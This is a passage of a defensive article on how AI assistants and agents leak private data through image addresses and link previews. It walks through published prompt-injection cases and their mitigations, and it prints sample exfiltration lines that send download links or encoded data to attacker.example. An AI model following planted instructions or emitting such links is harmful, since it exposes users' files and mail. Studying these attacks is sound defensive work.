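Suppose an answer takes eight seconds to stream and the model writes a complete image tag in the first second. The browser requests the image almost immediately. A sanitiser that runs only once the answer is complete is about seven seconds too late to stop that request.

A product could hold the whole answer back until the sanitiser has finished, but users like to see text appear, and long answers would feel slow. The better method is to clean every version of the answer before showing it:

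```
each time more text arrives:
    answer = answer + new text
    html   = convert_markdown(answer)
    html   = keep_only_permitted_images(html)
    show(html)
```

The sanitiser here checks the whole answer so far. If it checked only the newest piece, it could miss an address split across two pieces. It would also have trouble with the notation that got past Copilot's link filter, because that notation lets an image and its address arrive several sentences apart.

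The sanitiser also works on the HTML that the renderer produces from Markdown. Both Markdown notations become the same image tag, so the sanitiser doesn't need a rule for every way of writing an image. A filter that searches the Markdown has to cover every image notation that the renderer accepts, and whoever updates the renderer may not think to update the filter.

Developers can still get the order wrong, because a browser may request a picture as soon as a script creates its image tag, even if the tag never appears on the screen. The sanitiser therefore has to handle the HTML as plain text or inside a document the browser treats as inert, such as the one HTML's template element provides.

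A quick look at the finished answer won't reveal this fault; in SearchLeak, that answer showed a harmless block of code. The server-log test for public chatbots will catch it if the tester asks for a long answer with the image near the beginning. The test is worth repeating with the image's address on a separate line, because Copilot's filter handled one notation and missed the other.

### Salesforce and the domain that anyone could buy

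Salesforce sells software for managing customer records, and Agentforce is its platform for AI agents that work with those records. Many Salesforce users put a Web-to-Lead form on their public website. Whatever a visitor types becomes a record of a possible customer, known as a lead.

Sasi Levi of Noma Security, which named the flaw ForcedLeak, found that a visitor could type instructions for the agent into the form. Willison's note *ForcedLeak* explains that the agent did not act on them until an employee asked it about the visitor's lead. The agent then answered the employee and also followed the visitor's instructions to look up other leads' email addresses and put them in an image address. Infosecurity Magazine's *Critical Vulnerability in Salesforce AgentForce Exposed* gives the flaw a severity score of 9.4.

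Salesforce's CSP blocked images from unknown sites but still allowed my-salesforce-cms.com, a domain Salesforce had once controlled but whose registration had lapsed. According to Hackread's *ForcedLeak flaw in Salesforce Agentforce AI Agent Exposed CRM Data*, anyone could buy the domain for $5. The researchers bought it and received the lead data in their own server's log. Noma told Salesforce Ben, a news site for Salesforce users, that sending the data out "would have been impossible" without this gap in the policy.

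Noma reported the flaw on 28 July 2025 and Salesforce acknowledged it on 31 July, according to the timeline in Security Affairs' *ForcedLeak flaw in Salesforce Agentforce exposes CRM data via Prompt Injection*. Salesforce began enforcing a list of trusted addresses for its agents on 8 September, and Noma disclosed the flaw publicly on 25 September. The Hacker News (2025) reported that Salesforce also regained control of the expired domain.

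Taking back the domain closed this one hole, while the trusted list also removes unlisted addresses from the agent's answer. PromptArmor's *One key way Salesforce mitigates AI risk* describes how the chat inside Salesforce's web app now replaces any unlisted address with a placeholder before it displays the answer. The rule covers Markdown images, ordinary links, and addresses inside HTML and page styling. PromptArmor notes that this protects only one of Salesforce's many AI features, and that an agent with tools could still send data out in other ways.

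TechNadu's *Salesforce to Enforce Trusted URLs for Agentforce and Einstein AI* explains that each customer's administrators now have to add to the list every outside domain their agents need. An administrator who adds a trade fair's website and forgets about it can recreate ForcedLeak when the domain's registration expires. PromptArmor advises against wildcard entries that cover sites where strangers can post, and suggests leaving images off for each listed domain unless the agent has to show images from it.

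Salesforce also lets administrators replace names, email addresses, card numbers and similar details with placeholders before the text goes to the model, so the model can't leak the details that were replaced. This masking recognises only known patterns and fields that the company has labelled. It would miss a paragraph about a client's plans to close a factory, for example, so it reduces the damage but doesn't remove the need for an allowlist.

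Some products offer similar protection but let administrators choose a weaker form. In Glean, an assistant that searches a company's documents, the "Flag for review" option records a suspicious address but returns the answer unchanged. If the app showing the answer loads images, the data has already leaked by the time anyone reads the report. The redact option removes only addresses that Glean rates as medium risk or higher. Administrators can also exempt addresses that come from trusted tools. This is reasonable for an internal directory but much less so for a tool that returns incoming mail, because an attacker can put a whole set of ready-made links in an email.

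### Superhuman and the form that accepts an image request

Superhuman makes an email program with an assistant that answers questions about the user's mail. PromptArmor tested Superhuman's products in late 2025, shortly after Grammarly acquired the company. In PromptArmor's *Superhuman AI Exfiltrates Emails*, a user asks for a summary of recent mail and the assistant collects everything from the past hour. One of those emails contains hostile instructions, which PromptArmor hid in white text on a white background. PromptArmor notes that hiding them wasn't necessary, because the user never had to open the message.

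Superhuman's CSP blocked images from unknown sites but permitted docs.google.com, which also hosts Google Forms. The creator of a form can write a link that submits an answer when it is opened, and a browser loading an image sends the same kind of request as a browser opening a link. The assistant put the contents of the emails into such a link and presented it as an image. When the browser requested the image, Google stored the emails as a response to the attacker's form, so the attacker didn't need a server.

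Willison identified the CSP entry as the root cause. Anyone can create a form on docs.google.com and read what it receives. The domain still looks sensible on an allowlist because Google owns it and many people keep pictures in their documents.

PromptArmor extracted the full contents of several sensitive emails in one answer, including financial, legal and medical information, and partial contents of more than 40 emails in another. The user had asked one of the most common questions people put to an email assistant.

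PromptArmor found related problems in other products from the same company. Superhuman Go, an assistant that works alongside web pages and connects to services such as Gmail and Stripe, would load an image from the attacker's own domain, so the attack didn't rely on Google. In one test, a page of customer reviews made it leak financial figures from the user's mail. Grammarly's new document editor had a similar fault, but its assistant seemed to read only the open document and the user's questions, so there was much less to steal. The assistant in Superhuman's email program could also open any web address itself, so it could leak data without displaying an image.

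PromptArmor sent its report on the night of Friday 5 December 2025, and Superhuman acknowledged it the same day. On Monday 8 December the company switched off the vulnerable features, a sensible first step that protected users while engineers worked on lasting fixes. It released the first of these on 9 December and fixes for its other products on 18 December. PromptArmor reported more problems on 5 January 2026, Superhuman released further fixes on 11 January, and both sides had agreed to publication on 12 January.

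The same form trick worked a few months later against OpenAI's Codex, which by then handled everyday office tasks as well as programming. PromptArmor's *Codex Exfiltrates Connector Data* describes how a hostile email made Codex send the full contents of other emails to a Google Form through an image while it sorted the user's inbox. PromptArmor reported the flaw on 21 April 2026 and published it on 21 May, after OpenAI had fixed it.

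### The panel beside the inbox

Many email programs let people block outside images in incoming messages, since senders use those images to learn who has opened a message. A user or administrator who has turned this setting on may assume that it covers the assistant too.

There is no reason to expect a mail program's setting for images in open messages to cover the assistant's panel. The panel sits beside the inbox, but it displays the model's answer, as a chat window does, and it often has its own renderer. In the Superhuman attack, the hostile email stayed closed and the image was in the summary, so a setting for open messages would not have blocked it. In EchoLeak, the hostile text was also in an email and the image was in Copilot's answer.

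An administrator can check whether the setting that blocks outside images in messages also covers the panel by turning it on and running the same server-log test on the panel. If a request arrives, the setting doesn't cover the panel, and the company has to rely on the panel's own allowlist. The setting may still apply to email that an agent writes and sends, because that text ends up in a message.

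### What a sound allowlist requires

The domains that let data out had little in common apart from being on a list:

| Case | Permitted domain | Owner at the time | How the data reached the attacker |
|---|---|---|---|
| EchoLeak | teams.microsoft.com and subdomains | Microsoft | A Teams service fetched the attacker's address |
| SearchLeak | bing.com and subdomains | Microsoft | Bing's image search fetched the attacker's address |
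| ForcedLeak | my-salesforce-cms.com and subdomains | Nobody, until the researchers bought it | The request went straight to the new owner |
| Superhuman | docs.google.com | Google | A Google Form stored the request |

A company should start by allowlisting only domains it owns. That rule would have excluded docs.google.com and, if anyone had checked the registration, the lapsed Salesforce domain. But ownership is not enough, since Microsoft owned both Teams and Bing. Reddy and Gujral recommend allowlisting only the company's own addresses and using no wildcards. The ban on wildcards would have helped Microsoft more, because its single entry for all of Teams also allowed a forwarding service that had nothing to do with Copilot's images.

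The permitted address must also have no feature that records a request where an outsider can read it, or passes the request on. Questionnaires, storage that customers can rent and pages with visitor statistics all record requests. Link previews, translation tools, redirects and searches by image pass them on. Large general-purpose domains nearly always have something of the kind, and no one person knows every feature on them. It is easier to put the assistant's icons and pictures on a separate address that does nothing except serve files uploaded by staff:

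```
Content-Security-Policy: img-src https://icons.example.com/assistant/
```

The policy can name a folder, as it does here, but browsers ignore the folder after a redirect, so this server shouldn't redirect requests. If the model writes private data into an address on this server, the data ends up in the company's own log, which should have the same protection as the records the data came from.

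Some products have to show pictures from elsewhere, such as customers' logos. Reddy and Gujral propose a proxy that accepts only signed addresses. The company's server uses a secret key to calculate a code for each address it approves, and the proxy refuses any address without a valid code. The model doesn't have the key, so it can't approve an address of its own. The server must sign only addresses that the company has chosen in advance. If it signs whatever appears in the model's answer, the proxy will fetch an attacker's address, as the Teams service did.

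An allowlist also goes out of date without anyone editing it. Domain registrations expire, and a listed site can add a feature that forwards requests. Each entry should therefore record who is responsible for it, why it is there and when the domain's registration ends. In CSP's report-only mode, the browser reports what a stricter policy would have blocked but still loads it. The company can run a shorter list in that mode for a few weeks to see which omitted entries the product still uses, then delete the others.

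Every successful attack should prompt a review of which other entries on the assistant's allowlist can fetch a URL supplied by an outsider. After EchoLeak, Microsoft had 28 other entries on Copilot's list to check, and Bing was one that could fetch such URLs.

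## Email written by an agent: Copilot Cowork

The owner of an assistant's panel can set a CSP for it and clean the model's text before showing it. When an agent sends that text by email or chat, the recipient's mail or chat program displays it under its own rules about images, and the assistant's CSP has no effect there.

Copilot Cowork is Microsoft's agent for office work. Given a task, it writes documents, schedules meetings, sends mail through Outlook or posts in Teams. It can read whatever the user can open. Microsoft announced it in March 2026 and built it on Anthropic's Claude Cowork, according to ITPro's *Copilot Cowork is now generally available*. *Microsoft makes Copilot Cowork open to everyone* (Moore, 2026) reported its general release on 16 June.

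### A message to oneself

In May, while Cowork was still in preview, PromptArmor's *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Exfiltrates Files* described how an attacker could use it to steal a user's files. The user in the demonstration kept financial and personal records in SharePoint and OneDrive, Microsoft's services for shared and personal files. They had also given Cowork a skill they found online. A skill is a text file of instructions for a particular kind of task, and five of the 81 lines in this one were malicious.

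The user asked Cowork to review what they had worked on that week, and Cowork loaded the skill. It collected recently edited documents and obtained a download link for each one. Then it posted a recap to the user in Teams, with image tags like this one:

```
<img src="https://attacker.example/p.png?f=(download link for one file)">
```

When the user opened the message, Teams requested the images, and the attacker's server received the links. Cowork normally asks for permission before it sends anything, but PromptArmor found that it skipped this step when the user was the only recipient, and that users had no setting to change this. Cowork listed its completed actions, but the list never showed the hostile part of the message, even when the user clicked on the Teams step.

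Cowork runs code in a sandbox, an isolated environment that Microsoft intends to have no access to untrusted servers. The attack worked without breaching the sandbox because the user's own copy of Teams, not Cowork, contacted the attacker afterwards.

An outside image in a message can send data to whoever runs the image's server, even if the user is the only person on the "To" line. An exemption for messages to oneself is therefore risky, though it looks reasonable because the user already has access to everything in them. Willison (2026), in *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Exfiltrates Files*, called preventing this kind of leak the biggest continuing challenge in designing agents. Here the leak came from combining an agent that could message the user freely with a chat program that loaded any image it found, though each was harmless alone.

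### Why a download link is as good as the file

An ordinary link to a company file is of little use to a stranger, because the server requires visitors to sign in and checks whether they may open the file. A pre-authenticated download link contains its own proof of permission, so the server gives the file to anyone who uses the link, without checking who they are.

This means the length of an address no longer limits how much data can leak. Copying out a 20 MB presentation as text would take more than 3,200 images at Apache's default setting, and the model would have to write out every character. A download link fits in one address, however large the file is, and the attacker's computer can then download the file.

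Microsoft's developer documentation describes pre-authenticated download links as short-lived, so the attacker may get nothing if the user leaves the message unopened overnight. PromptArmor does not give the lifetime of the links it captured. But the user is likely to open a recap within a minute or two of asking for it, and a server can download each file as soon as its link arrives.

Administrators can stop Cowork from obtaining the links. PromptArmor's *Securing Microsoft Copilot Cowork* (2026), a guide for companies, recommends a SharePoint setting called Block Download for sensitive sites. With it on, people can view the affected files only in a browser and can't download, print or sync them, or open them in Word or Excel. The setting prevents the theft of whole files, but Copilot can still read them, so a hostile instruction could still lead it to copy a paragraph into an image address.

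### Five trials out of five

Cowork completed the whole attack in all five of PromptArmor's trials. The wording of the user's request made no difference as long as Cowork loaded the skill. With only five trials, the true success rate could plausibly be as low as 55%, but that would still be high enough to be useful to an attacker.

PromptArmor first tested Cowork's automatic setting, which chose between Anthropic's Claude Opus 4.7 and Claude Sonnet 4.6. It then selected Opus 4.7, the more advanced model, and the same hostile text worked unchanged. Opus 4.7 leaked more because it searched more thoroughly for recent work and included every document from that week's Cowork sessions. By the general release in June, Cowork was running on Opus 4.8 and Sonnet 4.6, according to ITPro, so Microsoft has replaced one of the tested models. That change offers little reassurance, because better models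 do assigned work more thoroughly, and here the model carried out the theft as part of its task.

The result is less surprising because the hostile text arrived in a skill, a file of instructions that the user has chosen to install. A model that follows a skill is doing roughly what skills are for, so one could fairly compare the attack to installing a malicious program. The user has not approved a stranger's email in this way, and models have become much better at ignoring instructions in ordinary outside text. PromptArmor says the attack does not depend on the source and names web pages and connected outside tools as alternatives, but the trials it reports used the skill.

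Still, people are less suspicious of a page of plain text than of a program, and their company has few chances to catch a malicious skill. Cowork automatically loads skills from a folder in the user's OneDrive, which limits administrators' oversight, and Microsoft does not check the skills that users add. PromptArmor's guide suggests that staff submit each skill for review before using it. A reviewer would have had to notice five lines out of 81, all about as long as the lines around them.

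PromptArmor's demonstration used Teams. The company says that opening such a message in Outlook can trigger the same requests, but it did not demonstrate this, and Outlook versions handle pictures differently.

### Microsoft's approval rule

Microsoft's *Application card* for Cowork, a document about the product's safety, calls the approval system its "primary safety mechanism". Microsoft's preview instructions stated the rule that PromptArmor tested, that Cowork "asks for your permission before taking sensitive actions", and gave sending an email and posting in Teams as examples. They did not mention an exemption for messages users send to themselves.

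A user had come across the exemption a month earlier. In *Cowork can't send emails?*, a post on Microsoft's community forum, VirginiaH1 (2026) complained that Cowork could send a test email to her own address but stalled on mail to anyone else because the approval prompt never appeared. Cowork's explanation was that messages to oneself seemed to be approved automatically. That is weak evidence, since a model can be wrong about its own software, but the behaviour she saw matches PromptArmor's finding.

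Microsoft's later descriptions of when Cowork needs approval are inconsistent. *Get started with Cowork* (2026), updated in August, requires approval for "Actions involving other people, such as sending emails or messages". Read literally, that excludes messages Cowork sends to its own user. *Copilot Cowork overview* (2026), from September, is broader: "You approve each action before it happens." An administrator can't tell from these pages whether Cowork still messages its own user without approval.

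Microsoft does not appear to have replied publicly to the finding or announced a change. PromptArmor presented it as a design risk rather than a bug, so there may never be a dated fix. PromptArmor's *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Controlled by Attacker, Bypassing Sandbox* describes a different flaw, which let code in a skill reach outside servers through Cowork's file-syncing service. PromptArmor reported that flaw on 24 June, and Microsoft confirmed on 19 August that it had fixed it. The fix concerned code in the sandbox and gives no reason to think that messages to oneself are now safe.

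Requiring approval for every message would help, but less than it seems. The approval dialog can preview the draft, but a one-pixel transparent image is invisible in a preview. If the preview loads outside images, the data leaves before the user decides, as happened with drafts in Notion's mail program. Users can also choose to skip further prompts for similar actions in the same conversation, an option that PromptArmor advises companies to forbid. Approval is good at catching a wrong recipient or an embarrassing sentence, but to catch images, the dialog would have to list every outside web address in the message, and even then a tired employee would probably press Send.

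### Tasks that run on a schedule

Cowork can also run a task repeatedly on a schedule. Microsoft gives the example "Send me a daily briefing every morning at 9 AM", which produces an email to the user written from their private mail and calendar entries. PromptArmor points out that the weekly review in its demonstration is the kind of task people would automate.

When a task runs on a schedule, nobody is watching, so nobody can press the pause button that Microsoft offers as a safeguard. One bad skill can also leak data from the newest documents on every run. Microsoft says that Cowork may ask for the approvals a recurring task needs when the user sets it up, so that it can run unattended later, which means the user approves messages before they are written.

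Since then Cowork has gained tasks that start when something happens, such as the arrival of an email. Microsoft's *What is New in Copilot Cowork* says that when one of these tasks involves sending a message, Cowork prepares it and waits for approval. This is the right rule if it covers messages to the user, but the announcement does not make clear whether it does. If it doesn't, an outsider could choose both the hostile text and when the agent reads it by sending an email.

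A scheduled briefing is safest when it contains nothing that needs approval. A daily summary needs only text and perhaps links to the user's own files, so the software that sends it can always remove images hosted on other people's servers.

### What mail programs do with outside images

Once the message has arrived, the reader's program decides whether to load the picture. The makers of the main mail programs have documented quite different defaults:

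| Program | Outside images by default | What contacts the image's server |
|---|---|---|
| Gmail | Shown, unless Google judges the message suspicious | Google's proxy |
| Classic Outlook for Windows | Blocked until the reader downloads them, with exceptions for trusted senders | The reader's computer |
| New Outlook and Outlook on the web | Shown | Microsoft's proxy |
| Apple Mail | Shown; loaded in the background if the reader has turned on Mail Privacy Protection | Apple's relays, or the reader's device without that protection |
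| Thunderbird | Blocked until the reader allows them | The reader's computer |

These are long-standing defaults, and an update, an administrator or the reader can change any of them. If staff read mail on both a computer and a phone, two of these rows may apply to the same inbox.

Image blocking protects readers from strangers who use images to track them, so both Outlook and Thunderbird let readers make exceptions for people they trust. An agent's message comes from the user's own account or a colleague's, so any such exception is likely to cover it. Even if the program blocks the images, a reader who sees one missing from their own weekly recap has good reason to click the button that loads it.

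These settings depend on whether the sender is trusted, but a model-written email from a trustworthy sender can contain a web address chosen by a stranger.

### What an image proxy hides

Gmail has loaded images through Google's own servers since 2013. When a reader opens a message, the page asks Google for the picture, and Google asks the server that holds it. Suppose that Ann's assistant has sent her a message with an image address that contains her private note. The attacker's log would look roughly like this without a proxy and with one:

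```
203.0.113.7     GET /p.png?q=QW5u...   Firefox on Windows
198.51.100.20   GET /p.png?q=QW5u...   image proxy
```

The proxy has replaced Ann's network address, which would have revealed her rough location, and the description of her browser and computer. It also keeps the other server from placing cookies (small identifying files) in her browser. The middle column is the same in both lines because the proxy has to ask for the exact address to get the right picture. It can't safely drop the part after the question mark, since many honest sites use it to select a picture or its size. As a result, senders may still be able to tell from unique image links whether someone has opened a message, as Google warns in its help for Gmail users.

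Attacks on Microsoft's products have shown the same limit in practice. In EchoLeak, the data left through a Teams proxy that fetches and caches outside images, as SC Media's *Microsoft 365 Copilot ‘zero-click’ vulnerability enabled data exfiltration* explains. In the newest case, some of the researchers who found EchoLeak, now at Cato Networks, published three more attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot on 3 December 2026 under the name ReLeak. In one of them, Copilot put confidential information in an image address, which Bing then fetched, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Three Zero-Click Vulnerabilities Discovered in Microsoft 365 Copilot*. Microsoft patched that route on 15 November, five months after it closed SearchLeak, which also went through Bing.

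A proxy may keep a copy of each picture, so that opening a message twice produces only one request, but one request is enough for the attacker. A proxy stops leaks only if it refuses addresses that the company has not approved in advance, as Reddy and Gujral's proposed proxy for signed addresses does. A public mail service can't refuse every picture it has not handled before.

Prefetching, which means loading something before the reader asks for it, makes this leak easier. Apple's Mail Privacy Protection, introduced in 2021, loads remote images in the background after a message arrives, even if no one opens it. Apple sends the requests through separate relays so that the image's server does not receive the reader's network address. This works well against marketers because every message appears to have been opened, so they can't tell which ones actually were.

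This setting does harm when a message has private data in an image address. The request goes out soon after the message arrives, so deleting an odd message unread is too late to stop the leak. A short-lived download link is also more likely to still work when it leaks. Someone who chose this setting for good reasons would have less protection against a leaking agent than someone using Thunderbird, and would not guess that from its name.

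Some software other than mail programs also fetches addresses before a person opens anything. In another of the ReLeak attacks, Copilot created files that contained hostile addresses, and Microsoft's own background processing visited them. The researchers reproduced this with Word, Excel, PowerPoint and PDF files, and Microsoft patched it on 11 November. Tests that cover only what happens when a person opens a message or a file would have missed this.

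### EFAIL, the same leak without a language model

In May 2018, eight years before Cowork, Damian Poddebniak and colleagues published EFAIL, an attack on the two main standards for encrypted email, S/MIME and OpenPGP. It could make a mail program put a private message into an image address. The attacker needed a copy of the encrypted message, perhaps from a hacked mail server, but not the key.

In the simplest version, the attacker sent the victim an email in three parts. The first part opened an image tag and began its address, the second was the stolen encrypted message, and the third closed the address and the tag. The victim's email program decrypted the message, joined the three parts into one web page, treated the secret text as part of the image address, and requested the image from that address.

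Another version changed the encrypted text itself. The encryption S/MIME used at the time did not detect tampering, so an attacker who could guess a few words of the original, such as its very predictable opening, could insert an image tag without being able to read the message. OpenPGP did check for tampering, but some programs displayed the text even when the check failed.

Poddebniak and colleagues found that 23 of the 35 S/MIME mail programs they tested, and 10 of the 28 OpenPGP programs, had channels that could leak decrypted text. Images were the most obvious channel, but style sheets and other parts of HTML could also trigger requests. As a short-term measure, the researchers advised people to decrypt messages outside the mail program or turn off HTML in it.

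Within two months, Apple and Mozilla, which then made Thunderbird, released fixes that stopped their email programs from joining decrypted text to the parts of the message around it. GnuPG, the most widely used OpenPGP software, began rejecting messages without tamper protection in June 2018. In 2019, a new version of the S/MIME standard added encryption that detects changes, and a revised OpenPGP standard did the same in 2024.

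These repairs did not block outside images, which Gmail and Apple Mail still show by default. That was sensible, because the fault in EFAIL was the mixing of text from two authors, and a mail program can keep encrypted and unencrypted parts separate. It can't do the same with an agent's message, because the model has already combined the private data and the attacker's address into one text from one sender. Even a fully repaired mail program will therefore load the image like any other. Encrypting the message would make no difference, since the program requests the image after decryption.

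### Which mail needs its images removed

The sending software is therefore the last place where a company can reliably stop the leak. What it should remove depends on what the model could read while writing the message and whether the message has any use for images.

Emails an agent sends to its own user should contain no images loaded from outside servers. Briefings, recaps and alerts draw on the most private material the agent has, and they lose almost nothing without pictures. If a weekly report needs a chart, the software can attach the image to the email, so displaying it sends no request to an outside server. A single summary of someone's mail can contain much of their mailbox, as Superhuman's assistant showed, and a scheduled briefing contains the same material every morning.

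Mail to a colleague or a customer needs the same treatment, although here there is a real wish for pictures, usually a logo and a signature. The company can have both by removing every image from the model's text and adding the logo afterwards from a fixed template:

```
html = convert_to_html(text_from_model)
html = remove_outside_addresses_that_load(html)
html = add_logo_and_signature(html)
send(html)
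```

The second step has to cover background images, style sheets and fonts as well as image tags, as EFAIL's list of channels suggests. Ordinary links can stay if the company accepts the risk that someone clicks one. Sending plain text is simpler, as long as the receiving program doesn't turn it back into images.

If an email to a customer leaks data, the sender will probably never know. The customer's email program requests the image, so nothing unusual appears in the sending company's network records, and the attacker also learns the customer's network address. Replies are a smaller problem. They usually quote the earlier message with its images, and the model could leak a little data by changing the image links or choosing which to keep, so it is easiest to strip images from the quoted text too.

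Bulk mail is the one case where outside images can stay, provided the model writing it has access only to public information. For example, a museum might have a model write its newsletter with access only to the exhibition pages on its public website. An attacker who got an image into the newsletter could still count readers, but would learn nothing else that the website does not already publish. To prevent the counting, the museum would do better to load pictures only from its own site. The mailing software should add subscribers' names and any personal links after the model has finished, so that the model never has access to the subscriber list.

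The museum's newsletter is safe because the model that writes it can't reach private data. That condition is easy to break with a general-purpose agent. Microsoft lists sending HTML newsletters among the things Cowork can do, but Cowork works with the user's full access to mail and files. Even a newsletter about the staff picnic counts as private mail here if Cowork writes it, because a malicious instruction in one of its sources could lead Cowork to search the mailbox.

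Before an agent gets permission to send anything, its administrator can repeat the server-log test with a message instead of a chat answer. They ask the agent to send them a message containing an image from a server they control, then check the log while the approval preview is on the screen, after the message arrives but before anyone opens it, and after opening it in Teams, in Outlook and on a phone. A request during the preview suggests that the preview loaded the image, and a request before the message is opened suggests that a program loaded it early. If the sending software removes the image as it should, the log stays empty throughout.

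## Messaging apps that preview links: OpenClaw on Telegram

In many messaging apps, an agent can leak data through a bare web address, with no image notation and before anyone clicks. Slack, Telegram and Discord show a small preview under a link, and a program has to open the link to make one. In email, a link sends nothing until somebody clicks it, so a company that strips outside images from an agent's emails can usually leave ordinary links in.

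### What happens before the preview appears

Suppose Ann's assistant posts this line in a chat:

```
Your summary is ready: https://attacker.example/s?q=QW5u...
```

The app finds the address, requests the page and looks in its HTML for tags that website owners add for previews. The usual tags, called OpenGraph, give a title, a description and the address of a picture, which the app also downloads. The attacker's page doesn't need these tags, because the app's first request has already sent Ann's note to the attacker.

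A chat message has room for the whole note. Slack's developer reference page *chat.postMessage method* recommends messages of up to 4,000 characters, almost twice the length of the address that held the note. Slack cuts messages off at 40,000 characters.

Slack also fetches links that it doesn't preview. According to Slack's *Unfurling links in messages* ("unfurling" is Slack's word for previewing), its servers must fetch every address in a message to learn whether it leads to a picture, a video or a page of text before Slack decides what to display. A message may therefore leak data even if no preview appears, so Slack's rule that messages with more than five links don't expand is not a safeguard. The setting described in Slack's *Share links and set preview preferences* that lets a reader hide previews isn't a safeguard either, because it changes only what that reader sees and Slack's servers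 still fetch the page.

Apps differ in which machine fetches the linked page to make the preview. WhatsApp and Signal have traditionally used the sender's device, which sends the preview with the message. MacRumors' *Link Previews in Popular Messaging Apps May Lead to Security Vulnerabilities* (2020) reported that Reddit's app used the receiver's device, which revealed the receiver's network address to the link's owner. Slack, Telegram and Discord use their own servers.

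Telegram's preview servers hide the reader's network address, as an image proxy does, but they also hide the leak from the company, whose network records show only normal traffic to a messaging service. Even a firewall that blocks the agent from every site except Telegram doesn't help, because the agent can still post the link, and Telegram's servers will then connect to the attacker's server.

Messaging services might also open links for reasons other than previews. In *A Black-Box Privacy Analysis of Messaging Service Providers' Chat Message Processing*, Kirchner, Koch and colleagues (2024) sent unguessable links through 105 messaging services and recorded visits to them. They found signs that 34% of the services analysed messages on their servers. Previews and checks for spam or malware could explain some of the visits, but one service made nearly 80 requests and another returned 30 days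 after the chat. The chats did not involve AI agents, but a service that opens links in people's messages has no obvious reason to skip an agent's. Turning off previews may therefore not stop all automatic fetches.

Rehberger described the danger of link previews for AI agents in August 2024, in Embrace The Red's *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks*. He posted a link to his own server through a Slack app and found a visit from "Slackbot-LinkExpanding" in the server's log. Willison (2024), in *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks*, wrote that he had not thought of link previews as a way to leak data before, although he had been writing about such leaks for more than a year.

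### An agent people talk to by text message

OpenClaw, formerly Clawdbot and Moltbot, is a free, open-source agent that people run on their own computers and instruct through a messaging app. It can browse the web, read and write files, keep a calendar and send email, according to Palo Alto Networks' *OpenClaw (formerly Moltbot, Clawdbot) May Signal the Next AI Security Crisis* (2026). By late January 2026, it had gained more than 85,000 stars on the code-sharing site GitHub, a rough measure of interest, in about a week. Microsoft warned companies in *Running OpenClaw safely* (2026) that the agent takes in untrusted text and has limited built-in security controls.

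In February 2026, PromptArmor's *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* showed that OpenClaw's default Telegram setup met all three conditions for a leak. Telegram fetched the agent's link for a preview as soon as the agent replied. PromptArmor's test site logged a request containing a person's name and an API key, a kind of password that one program uses to access another.

By default, a stranger who finds someone's OpenClaw bot on Telegram can't use it until the owner approves a pairing code, according to *Telegram*, the project's guide to the app. Pairing doesn't stop this attack, because the hostile text arrives in something the owner asks the agent to read.

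Governments noticed within weeks. The Hacker News' *OpenClaw AI Agent Flaws Could Enable Prompt Injection and Data Exfiltration* (2026) reported in March that China's national computer emergency team, CNCERT, had criticised OpenClaw's "inherently weak default security configurations". CNCERT advised users to run the agent in an isolated container, tighten network controls, keep passwords out of plain text files and install updates. This advice is sensible, and following it would leave fewer passwords to steal, but it doesn't stop Telegram from opening a link. Thailand's equivalent agency, ThaiCERT, did mention previews in its *Warning for OpenClaw Users* and pointed out that data could leave without a click.

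### What PromptArmor's public test found

PromptArmor also set up a website where anyone could test their own agent. A tester had the agent post a link to the site, which logged any request and the data in it. The log showed which program had fetched the page, such as Slack's or Telegram's, but not which agent had written the link, so testers "claimed" their log entries and named their agents. They could also report combinations of agent and app that produced no preview.

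The test has since closed. Wondrasek (2026), in *The Agentic Browser Attack Surface You Are Not Thinking About*, listed the main results on 24 February, while it was still running:

| App | Agent | Reported result |
|---|---|---|
| Microsoft Teams | Copilot Studio, Microsoft's tool for building agents | Preview fetched |
| Telegram | OpenClaw | Preview fetched |
| Discord | OpenClaw | Preview fetched |
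| Slack | The bot of Cursor, a programming tool | Preview fetched |
| Slack | Anthropic's Claude app | Lower risk |
| WhatsApp | OpenClaw | Lower risk |
| Signal | OpenClaw in an isolated container | Lower risk |

The two Slack rows suggest that an agent's maker can make a difference without any change to the messaging app. Slack lets each app installed in it turn off previews for its own messages, so the Claude app may have done that. The OpenClaw rows suggest that the messaging app matters too. On WhatsApp and Signal, the sender normally makes the preview. Here the sender is OpenClaw, so the page is fetched only if OpenClaw fetches it. PromptArmor did not report causes, so both explanations are guesses, and an update to the agent or the messaging app could change the result.

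The positive results are fairly solid evidence about the apps, because a request appears in the log only if something opened the link. They are weaker evidence about the agents, because nobody checked the testers' claims, and a tester could have named the wrong agent or pasted the link by hand.

The lower-risk results are even weaker evidence, because an empty log could mean that the app makes no previews for that agent, that the model did not write the link, or that the tester had already changed a setting.

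The test results can't be used to rank the pairings by danger either. Teams with Copilot Studio produced the largest share of fetches, which Wondrasek attributes to the number of companies using it. A popular pairing that leaks one time in ten can produce more log entries than an obscure one that leaks every time. The testers also chose to take part, and people who seek out a security test probably use a different mix of agents and settings from everyone else.

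The test covered only the automatic fetch. A preview in the log does not show that a hostile web page could have made the agent write the link. But a company deciding whether to put an agent in its chat mainly needs to know whether the fetch happens, and its own test will be more reliable than the public one. The administrator should ask the agent for a plain link as well as an image, use a new address each time in case the app keeps a copy of the page, and leave the log running for several weeks, because Kirchner and colleagues saw a visit after 30 days.

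### Turning previews off

For OpenClaw on Telegram, PromptArmor recommends one line in the configuration file, `~/.openclaw/openclaw.json`:

```
{ "channels": { "telegram": { "linkPreview": false } } }
```

With this setting, PromptArmor's test site stopped receiving data. OpenClaw's guide still described previews as on by default in August 2026, six months after the finding, so Telegram probably previews the agent's links unless the owner has turned previews off.

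The setting may also cover less than its name suggests. OpenClaw describes it as disabling "automatic entity detection for rich text", the step that turns a bare address into a link, but a link with its own label doesn't need that step. This matters most to owners who turn on OpenClaw's optional rich messages, which can include media, so they should test a labelled link and an image too. OpenClaw's tool for sending Telegram messages also accepts the address of a media file, which some program has to download, and the guide doesn't cover whether the preview setting affects this.

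On Slack, the developer of the agent has to set two options on every message:

```
{
  "channel": "C123456",
  "text": "(the agent's answer)",
  "unfurl_links": false,
  "unfurl_media": false
}
```

Rehberger recommended this in 2024, and Slack's documentation confirms that setting both to false stops its servers from crawling the link. Setting only one is not enough, because the first option applies to pages of text and the second to pictures, video and audio, and Slack has to fetch the link to determine which kind it leads to.

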